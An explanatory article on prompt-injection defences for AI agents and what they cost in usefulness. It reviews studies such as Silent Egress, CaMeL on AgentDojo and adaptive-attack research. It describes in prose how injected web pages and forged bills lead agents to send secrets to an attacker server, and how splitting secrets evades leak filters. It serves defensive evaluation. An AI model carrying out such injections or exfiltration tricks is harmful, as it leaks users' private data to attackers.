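Suppose a team tests three versions of Ana's agent on 100 attacks and 100 ordinary tasks, with these invented results:

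| Version | Successful attacks | Completed tasks |
|---|---|---|
| No restriction | 40 | 90 |
| Approved sites only | 5 | 75 |
| No outside requests | 0 | 50 |

The strictest version is the safest and the least useful. The best choice depends partly on how common attacks are, which benchmarks can't show because researchers decide how many to include. If one request in 1,000 contains an attack, 100,000 requests include 100 attacks. Limiting the agent to approved sites would prevent 35 leaks and break about 15,000 tasks, or roughly 430 broken tasks for each leak prevented. Blocking all outside requests would prevent only five more leaks and break another 25,000 tasks, or 5,000 for each additional leak prevented. A bank might accept that tradeoff, but a travel site probably wouldn't.

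Some studies also report how many tasks the agent completes during an attack, but a low number isn't always the defence's fault. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) describes a task in which the attacker's text replaces the contents of a bill the agent is supposed to pay. The agent couldn't complete that task under any defence, because the amount and the payee are gone.

### Silent Egress: blocking requests worked better than instructing the model

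In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) tested whether an agent built on qwen2.5:7b, a small open model, would leak a secret key. The user asked the agent to summarize a web page that contained instructions to send the key to the researchers' server. The researchers put the instructions in one of four parts of the page, delivered the page directly or through redirects, and told the agent to send the key whole or in pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times.

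The agent contacted the server in 423 of the 480 runs, or 88%. In 95% of the successful attacks, its final answer looked harmless. It never contacted the server in 120 runs with ordinary pages.

The researchers then tried several defences against the simplest version of the attack, with 30 runs for each:

| Defence | Runs in which a request reached the attacker |
|---|---|
| None | 100% |
| Telling the model never to follow instructions from web pages | 67% |
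| Marking web content as untrusted | 100% |
| Both of these | 57% |
| Domain allowlist | 0% |
| "Redirect detection" | 0% |

Instructing the model helped little, which fits the other evidence that labels don't reliably control which instructions a model follows. A larger model would probably have resisted more often, since this one was weak and the secret was in plain view.

The two zeros are weaker evidence than they seem. The allowlist contained four domains, and the attacker's domain, evil-collector.net, was not one of them, so the software was certain to block it. A real attacker would look for a listed domain that passes data on, as Aim did in EchoLeak. The "redirect detection" only matched address patterns. It blocked numeric addresses, certain domain endings and paths containing words such as "collect", which appears in the researchers' example of an attack address. An attacker could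 get around that last rule by renaming the page.

Lan and colleagues also didn't measure how many legitimate requests each defence would block. Three of the four permitted domains belonged to an imaginary company and the fourth was example.com, so an agent restricted to those domains couldn't open a news site. The experiment shows that a network rule can stop a leak the model doesn't prevent, but a team can't use it to decide how many domains to permit.

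### Why a 73% fall in measured leakage wasn't protection

Leak@1 is the share of runs in which the first outgoing request contains sensitive data. It was 96.7% when the agent sent the key whole and 26.3% when it sent the key in four pieces, a relative drop of 73%.

The attacker chose to split the key, so the fall shows how well the attack evaded the measure. Similarly, a filter that looks for email addresses in outgoing requests would catch "ana@mail.example", but the agent could send "ana@", "mail", ".exa" and "mple" in four separate requests. The filter would miss them because none is an email address, and the attacker could then join them.

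The agent contacted the attacker's server in 238 of 240 runs with a whole key, and still did so in 185 of 240 with a split one. The 22% fall happened because the small model sometimes failed to carry out the longer instructions. It is unclear how many of the 185 runs delivered every piece.

The 73% measurement is also doubtful. The paper reports that sensitive data appeared in the first three requests less often than in the first request alone, which is impossible under its own definition. A better measure would be whether the attacker ends up with the secret. An allowlist does well on that measure if none of its domains passes data on, because it blocks a four-character piece of a key as well as the whole key.

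### CaMeL stopped nearly every attack and broke many tasks

Researchers usually measure both attack prevention and usefulness with AgentDojo, a set of 97 tasks for simulated agents that handle banking, Slack messages, travel and office work. It pairs the tasks with prompt injections to make 629 attack cases. *AgentDojo* (2024) found that many of the defences it tested slightly improved task completion, presumably because they reminded the model of the user's request. But a filter for detecting injections raised so many false alarms that completion fell significantly.

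CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in 2025, restricts the agent much more. Suppose Ana asks her agent to send Priya the agenda from Tom's latest email. One model reads only Ana's request and writes a short program to carry it out. A second model extracts the agenda from the email, but it can't use any tools. Ordinary software runs the program and checks each action against policies about where its data came from. An instruction hidden in Tom's email therefore can't add a step or change the recipient.

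Ma and colleagues tested CaMeL on 57 of AgentDojo's tasks and 389 attack cases, using its creators' own code and policies:

| Model | Tasks completed without CaMeL | Tasks completed with CaMeL | Attack success without CaMeL | Attack success with CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o-mini | 66.7% | 26.3% | 58.6% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.4-mini | 77.2% | 52.6% | 6.9% | 1.8% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 63.2% | 28.1% | 50.4% | 0.3% |
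| DeepSeek V4 Flash | 89.5% | 38.6% | 22.6% | 0.8% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 70.2% | 40.4% | 0.3% | 0.3% |

CaMeL stopped nearly every attack, but agents completed between 32% and 61% fewer tasks. The benefit depended heavily on the model. Most attacks on GPT-4o-mini succeeded without CaMeL, and none succeeded with it. Claude Haiku 4.5 was no safer against these attacks with CaMeL, and its task completion rate fell by 30 percentage points.

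These results are worse than CaMeL's reputation suggests. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) describes its published results on AgentDojo as near-zero attack success with "still high utility". But *ATrust* (Zhang and Lu, 2026) also found a large loss, from 90.1% of tasks completed to 43.5% with the model Kimi K2.5, so weak models don't fully explain the results. Both retests come from researchers who had developed rival defences, so some caution is warranted.

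Claude Haiku's result also shows a limit of the test. *APPA* (2026) left AgentDojo out of its evaluation because leading models already resisted all the benchmark's standard attacks without any defence. With such a model, the test can measure only the usefulness lost to a restriction, even if that restriction would stop a new attack.

### Similar protection at half the cost

CaMeL's policy checks seem to provide much of its protection and cause much of its loss of usefulness. When *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) reran CaMeL with the checks off, 138 of 141 attacks in one category succeeded against one model. With the checks on, CaMeL blocked every attack but completed far fewer tasks.

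A better policy can recover some of the lost tasks. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) compared two on AgentDojo:

| Policy | Tasks completed | Attack success |
|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo's built-in defence only | 83.7% | 14.1% |
| With the FIDES policy | 33.2% | 0.6% |
| With a policy based on where data came from | 62.5% | 0.9% |

The FIDES policy labels information as trusted or untrusted and as confidential or public, and tracks those labels as the agent works. The agent completed nearly twice as many tasks under the other policy as under the FIDES policy, and the difference in attack success was within the margin of error. The comparison may be unfair to FIDES as a whole, because the system described in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025) can also hide selected information from the model.

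Labels make agents much less useful partly because they spread. If Ana's agent reads one confidential email, everything it writes afterwards may count as confidential, even an unrelated lunch order. Gregory, Domico and colleagues simulated this "label creep" in thousands of abstract tasks, without running a language model (*The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, 2026). Dividing the work among more agents limited the spread but could create many more connections to monitor. No arrangement prevented label creep entirely, so they concluded that such systems also need a safe way to remove labels.

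A narrower rule can avoid some of this loss of usefulness. ROPE, a defence by several of the *AutoDojo* researchers, blocks an action only if a sensitive detail, such as the recipient of a payment, comes from untrusted content and not from the user. With GPT-4o-mini, the agent completed 59.6% of tasks under ROPE, compared with 26.3% under CaMeL, though 6.4% of the standard attacks succeeded. OpenAI's and Anthropic's rules for web addresses are similarly narrow, because they restrict where an address may come from and leave the rest of the agent's plan alone. They may therefore reduce usefulness less than CaMeL does, but these tests didn't include them.

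### Tasks that change along the way

AgentDojo probably understates how much usefulness strict designs sacrifice. Li and colleagues found that only six of its 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan after it starts. An agent asked to pay a bill, for example, can plan in advance to read the file and then send the money. Real tasks are often less predictable. A checkout page might include an instruction to log in first, and the agent has to follow that instruction to finish the job.

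They built AgentDyn, a harder test with 60 tasks that all include helpful instructions of this kind and take seven steps on average. Zhang and Lu ran CaMeL on it with five models, and it completed none of the tasks, while the same models without a defence completed 18% to 72%. No attacks succeeded when they added them, but this is weak evidence of security because the agent did almost nothing. Ma and colleagues left CaMeL out of their own AgentDyn tests because it needs extensive policies for each setting. Missing policies might partly explain why CaMeL completed no tasks, but a company that adopted it would also have to write those policies.

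Zhang and Lu's own defence, ATrust, uses a trained model to pass on only the information the task needs. With GPT-4o on AgentDyn, it cut attack success from 37.8% to 4.4% and raised task completion from 53.3% to 63.3%. But its protection depends on a model's judgment. In a test with GPT-4o-mini, attack success rose from 3.6% to 12.1% when the attacker added a claim that the sources were trustworthy.

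An agent's usefulness under restrictions also depends on what it does after an action is blocked. In one of *APPA*'s tests, removing the agent's plans for recovering from a blocked action cut task completion to 35%, while attack success stayed at zero. OpenAI's software provides a simple form of recovery by prompting ChatGPT to try a different website.

### Attackers who adapt

AgentDojo's standard attacks are public and never change, so a defence can do well by recognising their wording. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested 12 defences with attacks adapted to each one, using automated searches and a contest with more than 500 participants. Reported attack success had originally been near zero for most of the defences, but the new attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them.

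One of these defences was Spotlighting, the technique Microsoft uses to mark outside text. The success rate of attacks against it rose from as low as 1% to more than 95%. Model Armor, a filter sold by Google, also failed more than 90% of the time. PIGuard did best among the filters but still let through 71% of attacks.

Nasr and colleagues gave their attackers large computing budgets and, when they attacked filters, showed them the filter's confidence score after each attempt, so the results show what a determined attacker can achieve, not how often ordinary attacks succeed. They didn't test CaMeL or rules that block network requests. Their evidence is strongest against defences designed to recognise malicious text or train the model to ignore it.

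Ma and colleagues did test CaMeL, with a weaker attacker that revised each attack six times and was told only whether it had succeeded. On GPT-4o-mini, PIGuard and CaMeL both stopped every standard attack, but the agent completed 43.9% of tasks with PIGuard and 26.3% with CaMeL, so a team that relied on the standard test would have chosen PIGuard. The revised attacks succeeded 28% of the time against PIGuard and never against CaMeL.

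One revised attack looked like an ordinary bill with a notice that the payee's account had changed. PIGuard detected no text resembling an instruction to an AI, and the agent paid the attacker.

Revised attacks worked especially well when the user let a document decide what the agent should do, for example by asking it to do everything on a to-do list. PIGuard let through 54% of attacks on such requests, compared with 17% when the user had specified every detail. The higher figure comes from only 24 attack cases, but the pattern makes sense. People use agents to avoid spelling everything out, and an attacker can supply the details they leave open.

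### What the Agents Rule of Two forbids

If a team can't rely on detecting injections, it can limit what an agent may do after one succeeds. Under the Agents Rule of Two, an agent that combines all three parts of Meta's broader version of the lethal trifecta in one session must be supervised, either by a person who approves its actions or through "another reliable means of validation".

Meta applies the rule to an imaginary email assistant, which a team could restrict in three ways:

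- It could read messages only from trusted senders, so it would miss an enquiry from a new customer.
- It could work without access to the real inbox, which makes it useful for little except testing.
- It could send messages only to trusted recipients or after the user has checked the draft, which costs the user some time.

The third option is best for most people. An agent can also change its permissions partway through a session. In Meta's example, an agent researches something on the open web, then permanently loses the ability to communicate before it opens internal systems.

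The rule doesn't depend on recognising an attack, so the results of *The Attacker Moves Second* don't undermine it directly. Its weak point is the exception for human approval. A team can satisfy the rule with a prompt that users approve without reading, as most of Anthropic's testers did with a dangerous command. Meta acknowledges this risk, and says the rule doesn't fit background agents well because nobody is there to approve their actions. OpenAI's Dots are background agents. Meta's article gives no attack success or task completion rates for agents that follow the rule, so a team that adopts it would have to measure for itself how much less useful its agents become.

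### What companies could measure

Anthropic's figures for auto mode include both the leaks it missed and the harmless actions it wrongly blocked. OpenAI's announcement of its index of web addresses gives no figures for false warnings, although the case for an index over a short list depends on how much those warnings inconvenience users.

A company can estimate how much usefulness a rule would remove before enforcing it. Browsers support a "report-only" version of a Content Security Policy, which reports each request the policy would have blocked but still lets it through. A team could run one for a week and check a sample of the reports to see how many of the images were harmless. It could also record which links and web pages a new rule would have stopped. The old protections would have to stay in place during the test, and the team would need to handle the records carefully because the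 addresses might contain private data.

Counting blocked requests would still understate how much usefulness a restriction removes. Once people learn that an assistant can't open their delivery links, many will stop asking it to, and the number of blocked requests will fall even though the assistant is no more useful than before.
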